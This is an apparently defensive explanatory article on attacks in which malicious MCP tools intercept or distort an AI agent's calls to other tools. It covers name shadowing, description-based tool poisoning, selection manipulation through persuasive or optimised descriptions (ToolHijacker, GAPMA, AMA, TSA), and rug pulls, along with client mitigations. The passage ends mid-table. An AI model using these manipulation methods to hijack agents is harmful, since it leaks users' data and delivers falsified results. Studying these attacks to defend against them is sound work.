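# Malicious tools that intercept calls meant for other tools in AI systems

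## How an AI system chooses and calls a tool

A language model produces only text. To let it send an email or look up an invoice, an AI application offers it *tools*, which are functions outside the model that it can ask the application to run. Each tool's publisher writes a *tool definition*, consisting of a name, a description and a list of parameters. The model reads the available definitions to pick a tool for each request. A dishonest publisher can therefore choose a name or word a description so that the model calls their tool for requests meant for someone else's, or uses someone else's tool wrongly. Both are forms of *interception*, which is any case in which a registered tool receives or changes a call that, given the user's request, should have gone unaltered to another tool.

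Many applications connect to their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, introduced in November 2024. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of 38 threats to the protocol, calls it the de facto standard. An MCP *server* is a program that offers one or more tools. The *client* is the part of the AI application that collects definitions from servers and sends the model's calls to them. MCP servers are usually programs that people install and run on their own computers (Willison, 2025, *Model Context Protocol has prompt injection security problems*).

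### One request, step by step

An office assistant might be connected to three servers. The company trusts its mail server, which offers `send_email`, and its accounts server, which offers `get_invoice`. An outside developer publishes the third, a notes server that somebody in the office installed for meetings. A user types, "find invoice 1042 and send it to Dana".

Before that request arrives, the client has already sent each server a `tools/list` message, and each server has replied with its definitions. The mail server's might look like this, in the format that Model Context Protocol's *Tools*, the relevant page of the specification, lays down:

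```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send an email from the user's account.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to": { "type": "string", "description": "Name or address of the recipient" },
      "body": { "type": "string", "description": "Text of the message" }
    },
    "required": ["to", "body"]
  }
}
```

A definition may also include a display title, icons, a schema for the tool's output, and *annotations*, which are notes on how the tool behaves. The specification requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. It has no such warning about descriptions, although the choice of tool depends mainly on the name and description. Tool names need to be unique only within one server, so the notes server can offer its own `send_email` tool.

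The client then adds the definitions to the model's *context*, the text the model works from. According to Anthropic's *Define tools*, the company's interface builds a system prompt from the tool definitions, the tool settings and the application's own instructions. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same arrangement for its models. Applications normally reserve the system prompt for their most authoritative instructions. It now includes the notes developer's sentences alongside the application's own instructions on every request, even when nobody wants a note.

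The model then outputs text that names a tool, `get_invoice`, and gives its argument, the number 1042. The client looks up which server offers a tool of that name and sends that server a `tools/call` message containing the name and the argument. The accounts server runs its code and returns the invoice, which the client adds to the context. The model uses this longer context to output a second call, `send_email`, with Dana as the recipient and the invoice in the body. The mail server returns a confirmation, and the model writes a closing sentence for the user.

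Tools in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) are designed to be "model-controlled", which means the model, rather than the user, chooses which one to call. The specification recommends, but does not require, that a person be able to deny a call and that the client show the inputs before sending them. Simon Willison advised treating these recommendations as requirements.

### Choosing among hundreds of tools

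The tool definitions from three small servers fit easily into a model's context, but those from larger collections do not. Anthropic's *Tool search tool* reports that the definitions for a typical five-server setup take up about 55,000 tokens (word fragments) before the model has done any work, and that Claude chooses markedly less accurately when it has more than 30 to 50 tools. OpenAI suggests making fewer than 20 available at the start of a turn. Large systems therefore split the choice into two stages. A search program called a *retriever* first selects a handful of definitions, and the model then picks a tool from among them.

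Shi, Yuan and colleagues (2025), in *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents*, write the two stages down exactly. Let q be the request and D the set of all definitions. An encoder f_q turns the request into a vector, a list of numbers, and an encoder f_d does the same for each definition d, in such a way that texts with related meanings get vectors pointing in similar directions. Sim measures how close two vectors are, for instance by the cosine of the angle between them. The retriever keeps the k definitions with the highest scores, and the model E picks one of them, d*:

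```
D_k = Top-k of Sim(f_q(q), f_d(d)), over all d in D
d*  = E(q, D_k)
```

In the second stage, the model receives one long string containing an opening instruction, the request, the k definitions, and a closing instruction.

Suppose the office assistant has five tools and k is 3. With invented scores for the request about invoice 1042, the retriever's work looks like this:

| Tool | Server | Similarity to the request | Kept? |
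|---|---|---|---|
| `get_invoice` | accounts | 0.81 | yes |
| `send_email` | mail | 0.72 | yes |
| `search_notes` | notes | 0.58 | yes |
| `list_customers` | accounts | 0.49 | no |
| `create_note` | notes | 0.31 | no |

The model's context now contains both tools that the request needs. If the notes developer rewrites the descriptions of `search_notes` and `create_note` to mention finding and sending invoices, their scores rise to 0.78 and 0.76. The top three scores are then 0.81, 0.78 and 0.76, so `send_email`, still at 0.72, drops out. The model cannot choose `send_email`, however careful it is, because it never receives the tool's definition. A publisher can therefore benefit from a retriever both by getting its own definition into the context and by pushing a rival's out.

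Commercial tool search differs from the formula in ways that matter to a defender. Anthropic's ready-made versions match text patterns, or rank definitions by the words they share with the query, and return three to five tools. Developers who want vector search build it themselves, and *Tool search with embeddings* (Keetay, 2025) shows how. The ready-made versions also search argument names and argument descriptions, so a reviewer who reads only the main description will miss text that can affect retrieval. Claude writes the query q itself, so the assistant might well search twice, once for invoices and once for email. An application can also keep some tools permanently in the context, which Anthropic recommends for the three to five most used tools to improve performance. This also improves security because a rival tool cannot crowd them out of retrieval, though the model could still choose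 the rival.

### What the model cannot check

The model receives a tool's definition before the call and the returned message after it, but the code in between runs outside the model. For example, the sample `send_email` function in OpenAI's guide prints its inputs and returns the status "sent" without sending anything. That is reasonable for a sample, but a model that receives "sent" from it has the same evidence as a model whose email was sent.

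A correct result doesn't show that a tool is safe. Willison gives the example of a tool that adds two numbers, posts the contents of a private file to an outside address, and returns the right sum. Shen and colleagues describe a `read_file` tool that returns the file and secretly copies it elsewhere. An output schema doesn't help much because it only fixes the form of a result, so an invoice with somebody else's bank account number passes the check.

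Tool definitions can also be used for *prompt injection*. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, uses the term for attacks in which a model follows instructions embedded in content it reads, as if the user had given them. These instructions are usually in emails or web pages, but the security company Invariant Labs showed in its *MCP Security Notification* (2025) that they can also be placed in tool descriptions, a technique it named *tool poisoning*. Tool descriptions suit this attack because the model receives them in full, while many clients show the user a shortened version or none.

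A model can obey a tool description written by a stranger because it does not distinguish data from instructions and only predicts the next token, according to Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), quoted in ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*. In SQL injection, by comparison, an attacker's input runs as a database command, which programmers can prevent by sending commands and data to the database separately. A language model receives both as one stream of text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, the NCSC concludes that design and operation can manage the risk but no product removes it. The evidence so far supports this. Dongol cites work by Nasr and colleagues in which attackers got past twelve recent defences by adapting to each one.

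Dongol contributes machine-checked proofs that injection causes no extra leaks in agents that fix their plan before reading anything untrusted. The proofs don't cover tool poisoning or agents whose model chooses every call, and both exclusions apply to the office assistant.

Some hostile tool definitions contain no injected instructions. A description crammed with search terms, or one that calls its tool the most accurate available, may still lead the AI system to choose that tool. A filter that looks only for commands will let such descriptions through.

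### Where a call can go astray

The journey of the request offers five openings, each with its own name.

| Point | What the attacker does | Result in the office assistant | Term |
|---|---|---|---|
| Installation | Publishes a server or tool under a name that resembles or anticipates a trusted one | Someone installs the wrong mail server | Tool squatting |
| Name | Gives a tool the name `send_email` | The client may send the email to the notes server | Name shadowing |
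| Retrieval and choice | Words a description to fit requests about invoices | The model picks a notes tool over `get_invoice` | Selection manipulation |
| Arguments | Writes about `send_email` in the description of a notes tool | The model calls the real `send_email` with a changed recipient | Description shadowing |
| After approval | Changes a definition or the code behind it | An approved notes server begins any of these attacks | Post-approval change, or "rug pull" |

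The two kinds of shadowing need separate terms because the literature calls both "shadowing". Invariant Labs used the word for cases where one tool's description affects how another tool is used. In its experiment, the coding assistant Cursor had a trusted email server and a malicious server whose only tool was described as adding numbers. That description also contained false information about how to address emails, and Cursor sent every message to the attacker, even when the user had named a different recipient. The attack did not depend on anyone calling the adding tool. Eight days later, Willison quoted Elena Cross, who used "shadowing" to mean that a malicious server overrides or intercepts calls to a trusted one.

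Shen and colleagues criticize earlier work for inconsistent terms, but their own catalogue gives "cross-server tool shadowing" two different meanings. The summary table describes it as a conflict of names, while the full entry describes hidden instructions that alter the use of another server's tools, with no shared name involved.

The term "tool shadowing" covers two attacks that need different defenses. In *name shadowing*, a malicious tool takes over another tool's name, which a client can prevent by keeping every name distinct. In *description shadowing*, a malicious tool's description changes how the model uses a different tool. Distinct names don't prevent this, because the call still goes to the right server under the right name, and only the arguments are wrong. Vendors who promise protection from "tool shadowing" should say which attack they mean.

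*MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) sorts attacks by the part of the system that can stop them earliest. It assigns tool shadowing and malicious registration to the *registry*, the catalogue in which publishers list their servers, and "selection inducement" to the client. The registry is a sensible first line of defence, but, as the paper also notes, it can judge only what a publisher submits, and a server may become malicious only after the review.

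### The attacker

The attacker is whoever currently controls the notes server. This may be the developer who wrote it, since anyone can publish a tool on an open platform, or someone who took it over later. Shen and colleagues describe one attacker who takes over a maintainer's account months after users approved the server, and another who buys the server's expired domain name. The attacker controls the notes server's definitions, its code and the messages it returns, but does not control the model, the client, or the mail and accounts servers, and has not broken into any of them.

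Attackers need to know little about the system they target. Shi and colleagues assume an attacker who knows what kind of task to capture, but who has no access to the users' wording, the other tools, the value of k, the retriever or the model, and cannot send the system test queries. This attacker tries out the attack on a replica they build themselves, which was good enough in most of the researchers' tests. Description shadowing also requires the name of the tool to be misused. An attacker can easily guess a name like `send_email`, and a public server gives its list of tools to any client that connects.

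In the attack flow of *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026), the user only has to connect the client to the malicious server and make a request. The client stores the tool descriptions without validating them, and the harmful call follows. The study scores tool shadowing at 21 points, a medium risk, compared with 42.5 for denial of service. Part of the gap comes from a score of zero that shadowing receives for being hard to discover. That score is odd, because Invariant Labs had already published the attack with a working example in 2025.

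The attacker's gain depends on which opening they exploit. A false `send_email` tool receives the call's arguments, so it collects the invoice and the name of the person it was for. Credentials are more valuable. In another Invariant Labs experiment, a poisoned tool led Cursor to hand over private login keys and a settings file of the kind that often holds passwords for other servers. The attacker may also want to trigger an action, such as sending an email from the company's own account, or to return a false answer. If a notes tool takes the place of `get_invoice` and returns invoice 1042 with a different bank account on it, the assistant will send that invoice to Dana through the genuine mail server, and every step after the first will work normally.

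## Duplicate tool names and how clients tell them apart

The simplest way for the notes server to receive an email meant for the mail server is to offer its own tool called `send_email`. The client then has two tool definitions with the same name, which is a *name collision*. If the collision causes the client to send the model's call to the notes server, it is called *name shadowing*.

Most collisions are probably accidents, because programmers tend to pick the same obvious names. Microsoft's *Tool-space interference in the MCP era* (2025) covered 1,470 working servers from two public registries and found name collisions for 775 of the 12,643 tools surveyed, about 6%. The most common was `search`, which 32 servers offered. Eleven servers offered `execute_query`, nine `send_message` and eight `execute_command`, and calls to these three can carry sensitive material.

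If someone picked eight of these servers at random, the chance that two of them would offer `search` is about 1%. The real chance is likely higher because people choose servers for related work. `send_email` is not among Microsoft's ten most common collisions, so at most eight of the servers offered it. A second `send_email` in the office assistant is therefore unusual enough to investigate, but it doesn't prove an attack.

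### What clients do with a duplicate

When two tools share a name, a program that stores its tools in a table indexed by name will replace the first with the second unless its developer adds a check. Other programs keep the first and discard the second. Vaughan notes in *MCP Tool Namespacing and Wall Time Tracking in Codex CLI* that some frameworks use whichever server connected first. Either way, the order of registration determines which tool receives the call, and users rarely know that order.

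In May 2026, Imoto's *I Wired 8 MCP Servers Into One Claude Agent* reported silent overwriting in Claude. The eight servers offered 87 tools, and three pairs of servers shared a tool name. Calls to `create_issue` meant for GitHub went to Linear, another issue tracker, where one exposed details of a private database in a client's project. According to Imoto, 22% of calls reached the wrong server.

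Anthropic's documentation contradicts this account, at least for Claude Code, the company's coding agent. According to Anthropic, Claude Code names every tool from an MCP server in the form `mcp__<server>__<tool>`, so the two tools would have been `mcp__github__create_issue` and `mcp__linear__create_issue`. Microsoft had already described this prefixing in 2025. Imoto's remedy was a setting called `tool_prefix`, which does not appear in Anthropic's reference page for connecting servers to Claude Code. Imoto also cites a March 2026 protocol revision, but Anthropic's page lists none between November 2025 and July 2026. The symptoms don't quite fit the explanation either, because overwriting would have sent every `search` call to the same server, and Imoto saw them go sometimes to one and sometimes to the other.

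The report is weak evidence about Claude Code because the configuration file in it belongs to Claude Desktop, a separate application that Imoto may have been describing instead.

There is better evidence of misrouting in Cursor. In *CRITICAL BUG*, a thread on Cursor's forum, staff confirmed that commands were going to the wrong servers and suggested running one server at a time or renaming them. Cursor adds prefixes in the form `mcp_<server>_<tool>`, but *Cursor MCP client confused by multiple tenants of same system*, a user report from January 2026, describes all calls going to one of two servers even though their prefixes differed. That diagnosis came from the AI model inside Cursor and needs confirmation, but it is worth testing whether the code that sends the call uses the prefix, because the prefix doesn't help otherwise.

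Some software refuses duplicate names. OpenAI's Agents SDK, a library for building agents, raises an error. Anubhav200311 (2026) explains in *Fix/deduplicate tool names* that Anthropic's interface rejects any request containing two tools with the same name. An error keeps the email from reaching the wrong tool, but it also lets the notes developer stop the whole assistant by adding one tool. Anubhav200311 proposed changing Docker Agent, the affected program, to keep the first tool and log a warning. The assistant would then keep working, but calls would again go to whichever tool was registered first.

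Most of the well-known clients rename tools instead:

- Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, originally joined the names as Claude Code does. If two joined names were identical, it skipped the later tool and wrote a warning to its log, as the code in *[MCP] Sanitize MCP tool names to ensure they are compatible* shows. Since 15 April 2026 it has registered every MCP tool under a namespace taken from the user's configuration file, according to Vaughan.
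- Zed, a code editor, lets its built-in tools keep their names and adds a prefix to tools from servers only when names clash. If the prefixed name is also taken, Zed drops the tool. Fenner and Brandt, in *agent: Ensure tool names are unique*, set out these rules.
- Spring AI, a Java framework, puts a counter in front of any name that is already in use, as Tzolov, in *Class DefaultMcpToolNamePrefixGenerator*, documents.
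- VS Code and GitHub's Copilot CLI write the server and the tool with a slash between them, according to *MCP Tool Naming*, a page of tips for developers.

If the user has called the notes server `notes`, its `send_email` tool ends up with these names:

| Client or framework | Resulting name | When it applies |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | `mcp__notes__send_email` | Always |
| Codex CLI | `send_email` in the namespace `notes` | Always, since April 2026 |
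| Cursor | `mcp_notes_send_email` | Always |
| VS Code | `notes/send_email` | Always |
| Zed | `notes_send_email` | Only if another tool has the same name |
| Spring AI | `alt_1_send_email` | Only if the name is already in use |

Spring AI's default is the least helpful for security because the name `alt_1_send_email` doesn't identify a server, and the first tool to register keeps the plain name. If the notes server connects first, its tool keeps the name `send_email` and the company's real mail tool is renamed `alt_1_send_email`.

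### What the specification requires

The Model Context Protocol specification of 28 July 2026 does not require clients to handle duplicate tool names in any particular way, but it recommends that clients combining several servers use some way of telling tools apart, such as a prefix that identifies the server. It also advises against relying on the name that a server reports for itself in the `serverInfo` field, because two servers may report the same name. The draft current in December 2026 has the same wording.

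The advice about `serverInfo` matters for security because the notes developer can type "mail" into that field. A client that built its prefixes from the field would then label the notes server's tool `mail__send_email`. Microsoft suggested in 2025 that clients generate namespaces from server names, which is safe only if those names come from the user's own configuration.

The previous revision of the Model Context Protocol specification, from November 2025, already limited the uniqueness of tool names to a single server but gave no advice on collisions between servers. The accepted proposal on tool names, SEP-986, asked for names to be unique "within their namespace" without defining a namespace. Its entry under security implications is "None". One of its aims was to allow names with levels, such as `admin.tools.list`, and the current specification still lists that name as a valid example.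 Nobody checks the part before the first dot, so the notes server could publish a tool called `mail.send_email`.

Microsoft called for formal namespaces in 2025, and Imoto mentioned a pending proposal for server-supplied prefixes. The July 2026 revision has no namespace field in its tool definitions. Server-supplied prefixes would prevent accidental duplicates, but they would stop a dishonest publisher only if somebody verified who owned each prefix, which is a job for registries.

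WebMCP is a proposed standard that lets web pages register tools with an agent in the browser. Every ordinary web page has an *origin*, which consists of the scheme, host name and port of its address. The browser determines the origin, so publishers cannot simply make one up. If the agent stores each tool under its page's origin, a `send_email` tool from a notes website cannot replace one from a mail website. However, an origin doesn't show that a site is honest. Any outside script that a site loads directly into its page also runs under that site's origin, so a compromised advertising script on the mail website could register tools under the mail website's origin.

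### How to keep names apart

A client that connects to several MCP servers can prevent name shadowing with five measures:

1. Assign each server an identifier in the client's own configuration, such as `mail`, `accounts` or `notes`, and ignore the name the server reports.
2. Put the identifier in front of every tool name, whether or not the name clashes.
3. Check the finished names for duplicates at start-up and whenever a server changes its list, and refuse any duplicate.
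4. Compare the original names in a simplified form, without differences of case or punctuation, and have a person review any match with a sensitive tool.
5. Show the server's identifier wherever a user sees or approves a call.

How far the identifier can be trusted depends on the configuration file it comes from. Claude Code reads server entries from several places, and if two entries have the same name, it uses the one from the higher-ranking source. A project's configuration file, which may come with downloaded code, ranks above servers the user has set up for all projects. A downloaded project that defines a server called `mail` can therefore replace the user's own `mail` server while that project is open. A rule that allows `mcp__mail__send_email` would then presumably also allow the replacement server's `send_email` tool.

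Anthropic has added some protection against this. Claude Code shows a warning in its server list when the two entries have different addresses, and in ordinary interactive sessions it asks for approval before using a project's servers. Automated runs load those servers without approval unless the operator restricts Claude Code to servers named on the command line. An organization can also provide its mail server through managed settings, which take precedence over every other source. Narrative's *Duplicate Tool Alias* describes a simpler rule, under which the company's interface rejects any request that gives two servers the same identifier.

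Adding prefixes only when names clash, as Zed does, has two drawbacks. The notes developer can change the name of the company's tool from `send_email` to `mail_send_email` just by offering a duplicate, and any permission rule written for the old name may stop matching. A server can also choose a name that already looks prefixed. If the client drops whichever tool ends up with a name already taken, it may drop the genuine one. Prefixing every name avoids both problems.

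A check at start-up misses duplicates that appear later, because a server can announce a new list of tools while the program is running. Anubhav200311 lists this among the cases that Docker Agent did not handle. Claude Code fetches the new list automatically. Microsoft found that only 226 of the servers in its survey declared that their lists could change, but any server can change its list without declaring it. When the check finds a duplicate, the client should exclude the less trusted server's tool and keep the rest running, so that the notes developer cannot shut down the mail server too.

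The fourth measure is needed because the specification treats names as case-sensitive, so `send_email` and `Send_Email` are different tools. The following table compares four possible names for the notes server's tool with the genuine `send_email`:

| Notes server's tool | Exact match? | After replacing forbidden characters with `_` | In lower case, without punctuation |
|---|---|---|---|
| `send_email` | Yes | `send_email` | `sendemail` |
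| `send.email` | No | `send_email` | `sendemail` |
| `Send-Email` | No | `Send-Email` | `sendemail` |
| `send_mail` | No | `send_mail` | `sendmail` |

Comparing simplified names catches the first three but misses `send_mail`, which needs a comparison that allows for small spelling differences. The client should use simplified names only for this check and send calls under the exact name. It also makes sense to limit the review to tools that send, pay, delete or reveal something. In Microsoft's count, harmless tools share names often enough that banning every match would be impractical.

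The fifth measure is to include the identifier, and preferably the server's address, in approval prompts. When Fenner first added prefixes to Zed in *agent: Namespace MCP server tools*, the interface still showed the name the server had supplied. A person asked to approve `send_email` can't tell from that name whether the message will go to the mail server or the notes server.

### Where prefixes fail

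Joining two names with a separator can produce the same result from different parts. Suppose server `a` offers a tool called `b__c`, server `a__b` offers a tool called `c`, and the client joins names with two underscores:

```
a     +  __  +  b__c   =   a__b__c
a__b  +  __  +  c      =   a__b__c
```

If two tools had the same name, Codex CLI's original code would have kept the one it processed first and skipped the other. This avoids accidentally sending a call to the wrong server, but it makes one tool unavailable and reports this only in a log. A client without this check could send the call to either server.

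Two different pairs of server and tool can never give the same joined name if server identifiers contain no double underscore and don't end in an underscore, because the first double underscore then always marks the boundary. The second condition is needed because server `a_` with tool `b` and server `a` with tool `_b` both become `a___b`. Cursor's format uses a single underscore, so its identifiers would have to contain no underscores at all. The easiest rule for an administrator is to use only letters and digits in server identifiers.

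A more reliable design stores the server and tool names in separate fields and uses the joined name only as a label for the model. The client looks up the label in its table and reads the server from the entry, so it doesn't have to split the label. *MCP Tool Namespace Unification* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a data type in Codex CLI that now keeps the two fields separate. Previously, different parts of the program stored names in different formats, and a mismatch could make a tool impossible to find without producing an error.

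Replacing characters can also make two names identical. OpenAI's interface accepts only letters, digits, underscores and hyphens, so Codex CLI replaces any other character with an underscore, and `foo.bar` becomes `foo_bar`. According to a comment in the code, a *hash*, a short code calculated from the full original name, will keep such tools apart. But the lines added with that comment calculate a hash only for names that are too long, which is a good reason to test a client's behaviour rather than rely on its comments.

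Server identifiers have the same weakness. The first version of *feat(mcp)* (2026), a proposed change to OpenAI's Agents SDK, checked for duplicates before adding the prefixes. Servers called `a-b` and `a_b` then received the same prefix, and one server's tools silently shadowed the other's. The developer fixed this by repeating the check after adding the prefixes.

Shortening names to fit a length limit can cause collisions. Zed limits names to 64 characters, and one of its tests uses a 34-character tool name. With the underscore, this leaves 29 characters for the server's identifier. Two servers whose identifiers begin with the same 29 characters would get the same full name for that tool. Zed's check would miss this collision because it compares prefixed names with the original names, not with each other.

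Codex CLI shortens a long name and adds a hash of the original, which keeps different names distinct. Cursor does the same, according to a staff reply in *PostHog MCP Tool Names Too Long*, and limits the combined server and tool names to 60 characters. A person can't identify a tool from the hash, so an approval prompt should still show the full name.

Claude Code leaves out any tool whose full name is longer than 128 characters, and the server's other tools keep working. Earlier, yautja_cetanu, a developer of Drupal's MCP software, reported that a tool name of just over 50 characters caused errors because Claude Code's prefix took it past a 64-character limit. MintMCP's *MCP fixes and known issues in Claude* describes a more serious earlier fault, in which a single overlong name from any connected server stopped the entire Claude environment from working. The same page reports that from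 July 2026, Claude's web and desktop applications intermittently kept only the first 256 tools in alphabetical order. During that fault, a server with hundreds of tools and an identifier early in the alphabet could have pushed out the other servers' tools.

Security rules can also stop working when names change. In Claude Code, the prefix of a tool from a plugin's server also includes the plugin's name. An administrator can set up a *hook*, a script that runs automatically at certain points, to inspect each call to a server. If the hook's pattern contains only the server's name, the hook never runs for the plugin's version of that server, and Claude Code makes the calls without inspecting them. Vaughan reports that a reviewer of Codex CLI's change also worried that namespaced tools might bypass a restriction meant to limit certain operations to one built-in tool. Anyone who adds or changes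 prefixes should test every rule that refers to a tool by name.

### Which tool the model prefers

With correct prefixes, a call to `mail__send_email` reaches the mail server, but the model may still call `notes__send_email` instead if both are available. Both names are valid, both tools appear to send email, and the user's request didn't mention a server.

Imoto (2026) came to the same conclusion in a reply under the original article, *MCP Tool-Name Collisions*, explaining that the prefix had turned one ambiguous `search` into two valid options. Rewriting the descriptions to state whether each tool searched local notes or the public web had helped more. That works when the same person controls both descriptions, or when both publishers are honest. But a dishonest notes developer can make the description of `notes__send_email` as persuasive as they like.

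Tools with different names can compete in the same way. Microsoft lists 23 names for tools related to web search, including `websearch`, `web_search`, `search_web` and `google_search`. A check for duplicate names would not flag these, and a model could reasonably pick any of them to search the web.

For sensitive actions, the safest approach is to give the model only one tool that can perform them. Codex CLI lets users list the enabled and disabled tools for each server and applies the disabled list last, as an example in OpenAI's *Model Context Protocol* shows. The office could disable `send_email` on the notes server and keep the note-taking tools. In Claude Code, withholding permission from a tool blocks calls to it, but the model can still see the tool and may waste a turn trying to use it. Approving everything from a server with a wildcard such as `mcp__notes__*` is convenient but also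 approves any tool the notes developer adds later. If users list approved tools by name instead, a new `send_email` won't run until someone allows it.

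## Tool descriptions written to win selection

In *selection manipulation*, a publisher words a tool's definition so that the model is more likely to choose that tool for certain requests. The tool can then receive calls meant for another tool, even if no other tool has the same name. Suppose the developer of the office assistant's notes server offers a tool called `find_records` and describes it as a dependable way to look up invoices and payments. When a user asks for invoice 1042, both `get_invoice` and `find_records` fit the request, and the model can compare only what their publishers wrote. If it chooses `find_records`, the notes developer receives the request and can return a false invoice.

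The attacker usually aims at one kind of request. Users phrase the same request in many ways, so the description has to win for as many wordings as possible. Let q_1 to q_m be differently worded requests for one task, D the definitions of the other tools, and d the attacker's definition. With the retriever (Top-k) and the model (E) of the two-stage selection process, the attacker's objective is:

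```
maximise over d:  (1/m) · Σ [ E(q_i, Top-k(q_i; D ∪ {d})) = d ],   i = 1 to m
```

The square bracket counts as 1 when the model picks the attacker's tool and as 0 otherwise, so the whole expression is the *attack success rate* for that task. If the notes developer tries 20 ways of asking for an invoice and the model picks `find_records` for 17 of them, the rate is 85%. In a system without a retriever, the model receives every definition, so there is no Top-k step.

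Published success rates measure only how often the model selects a malicious tool that is already installed. According to *MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026), a complete attack also requires a user to install the tool and the tool's code to do something malicious.

### ToolHijacker

Shi and colleagues introduced this attack in 2025 as ToolHijacker. They divided the false tool's description into two parts. The first part is written so that the retriever selects the tool. To produce this part, a language model reads five sample requests and describes a tool that could answer them all, which makes the text similar in meaning to other requests for the same task.

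The second part is written to make the model choose the tool. The attacker uses one language model to generate wordings, tests them on the sample requests in a replica of the target system, and carries the best into the next round. For one task, this search took only 12 model queries. Another version uses the gradients of open models, which show how changing a word would affect the outcome. It did better than the first version on most of the open models but was usually a little weaker on the commercial ones.

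The researchers used two collections of tools. MetaTool has 199 tools, taken from OpenAI's plugins, and ToolBench has 9,650 from RapidAPI, an online marketplace. For each collection they chose seven tasks and wrote 100 requests for each task. Without an attack, the eight models they tested picked a correct tool for 87% to 100% of requests. With one false tool added, the version without gradients had these success rates on five of the models:

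| Model | MetaTool | ToolBench |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 96.4% | 85.1% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 92.4% | 92.0% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 83.4% | 79.6% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 99.7% | 89.0% |
| Llama 3 70B | 98.1% | 77.6% |

A large collection of tools gave little protection. The malicious tool ranked in the retriever's top five for 95% of ToolBench requests, even though the collection held 9,650 other tools.

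Shi and colleagues also tested each part of the description alone, on one MetaTool task with GPT-4o. The retrieval part always got the tool into the retriever's top five, but the model chose it for only 5% of requests. The selection part got the tool into the top five for 65% of requests, and the model chose it for 63%, nearly every time it appeared there. An attacker would therefore still get most of the requests if the retriever missed the false tool a third of the time. With both parts together, the model chose the tool for 99% of requests.

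The attack was also narrow. The researchers tested a description optimised for one task on 600 requests for six other tasks, and the model never chose the false tool. In the office assistant, `find_records` could capture every invoice request while emails, notes and customer lists kept working normally, so users would have little reason to suspect it.

### Advertising in place of commands

ToolHijacker's descriptions contain conspicuous orders to choose the tool. Ordinary promotional language can also work, as Faghih, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Gaming Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs*, found when they offered models pairs of identical tools and edited the description of one. They ran every test in both orders, because models tend to favour whichever tool comes first. Averaged over ten models, the tools received these shares of correct use:

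| Addition to the description | Edited tool | Original tool |
|---|---|---|
| Assertions of effectiveness or priority | 81.8% | 7.3% |
| Claim of active maintenance | 61.8% | 30.5% |
| Name of a famous company or person | 55.1% | 39.4% |
| Usage example | 53.2% | 31.5% |
| Number of users or stars | 51.8% | 43.6% |
| Longer text | 48.1% | 39.0% |

The two shares need not add up to 100%, because a model could call both tools or call neither correctly. A dishonest publisher can easily make most of these additions, since the model cannot check them. Usage examples, however, help the model use a tool properly, and MCP recommends them, so an honest publisher who documents a tool well will also win more requests. This makes it hard to define manipulation by its effect alone.

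*MPMA* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2025) studies sellers of paid MCP servers who want more calls than their competitors. The simplest version of its preference manipulation attack puts a superlative at the start of the tool description, which won the seller every request in almost all settings. A reviewer would notice the superlative, so the researchers developed a subtler version, GAPMA. GPT-4o rewrites the description in one of four advertising styles (authoritative, emotional, exaggerated or subliminal), and a genetic algorithm then repeatedly varies and combines the results, keeping those that look least suspicious.

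Each test had one manipulated server and five competitors with the same function. Across eight functions and four styles, GAPMA won 91.9% of requests on Gemini 2.5 Flash, 78.8% on DeepSeek-V3, 73.8% on Qwen3-235B, 62.8% on Claude 3.7 Sonnet and 22.2% on GPT-4o. The authoritative style, which presents praise as expert opinion, was the strongest overall and won at least 95% on every model except GPT-4o.

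Manipulation may become less effective when many servers use it. When six of eight competing servers used these techniques, DeepSeek, Claude and Gemini chose an unmanipulated server every time, and their replies cited its straightforwardness as the reason. GPT-4o and Qwen3 still chose manipulated servers. The test covered only servers that tell the time, so the result is too narrow for defenders to use.

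*Attractive Metadata Attack* (Mo, Hu and colleagues, 2025) describes an attack, AMA, that changes a tool's name and parameter list as well as its description. A language model generates a batch of false tools, the researchers measure how often a test agent calls each one, and the most frequently called become the starting point for the next batch. The researchers tested the resulting tools in ten simulated workplaces on Gemma 3 27B, Llama 3.3 70B, Qwen2.5 32B and GPT-4o mini.

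When the attacker knew the field of work and its tools, the models called the false tool in 81% to 96% of cases. Without that knowledge, they called it in 23% to 83%. These numbers are not directly comparable with ToolHijacker's, because an agent in these workplaces could call several tools for one job. The three open models completed at least 97% of their tasks when the attacker had this knowledge, so they often called the false tool in addition to a genuine one rather than in its place.

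An extra call to a false tool is enough to leak data. Each agent had a fictitious user's personal details, and its system prompt prohibited disclosing them. The false tools listed such details as parameters, and in the informed tests the models filled in 81% to 95% of what the attacker asked for. If `find_records` had a parameter for the customer's home address, the assistant might fill it in simply because it was listed.

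### The tool-spoofing study of October 2026

Dai, Sun and Tao (2026), in *Spoofing the Toolbox*, set out to combine ToolHijacker's success rate with language that arouses no suspicion. Their attack, TSA, maximises the same success rate under the added condition that the false description stays close in meaning to the genuine one. The attacker never has access to the target system and works on a replica:

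1. A small language model, Qwen3-8B, writes ten variants of the genuine description. Eight include a sentence urging selection and two do not.
2. A test agent running Llama 3.3 70B receives a request, the genuine tool, the false tool with one of the variants, and several unrelated tools.
3. The program records whether the agent picked the genuine tool, the false tool, an unrelated tool or none. It also calculates the variant's *perplexity*, which measures how improbable a language model finds a text. Natural sentences usually have low perplexity.
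4. Qwen3-8B rewrites the variants, with earlier successes and failures as examples. It makes bigger changes while nothing works and smaller ones after a success.
5. After several successes in a row, the search stops and the program keeps the successful description with the lowest perplexity.

The search took an average of four and a half minutes per task. Its success depended heavily on the examples and the adjustable size of the changes. A basic version that only rephrased the description, using a single request and a fixed set of tools, reached 40%, compared with 88.7% for the full attack.

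The main tests used TSABench, a new collection of 144 tools from real MCP servers. The researchers generated ten requests for each tool, used seven for the search and kept three for the test. They removed requests that named a tool. They compared TSA with ToolHijacker, GAPMA, AMA and a *tagged copy*, the genuine description inside a tag that marks it as important. They also asked people to rank the descriptions from 1 (most suspicious) to 6 (least suspicious).

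| Description | Llama 3.3, 10 tools | Llama 3.3, 20 tools | GPT-5, 10 tools | Average human rank |
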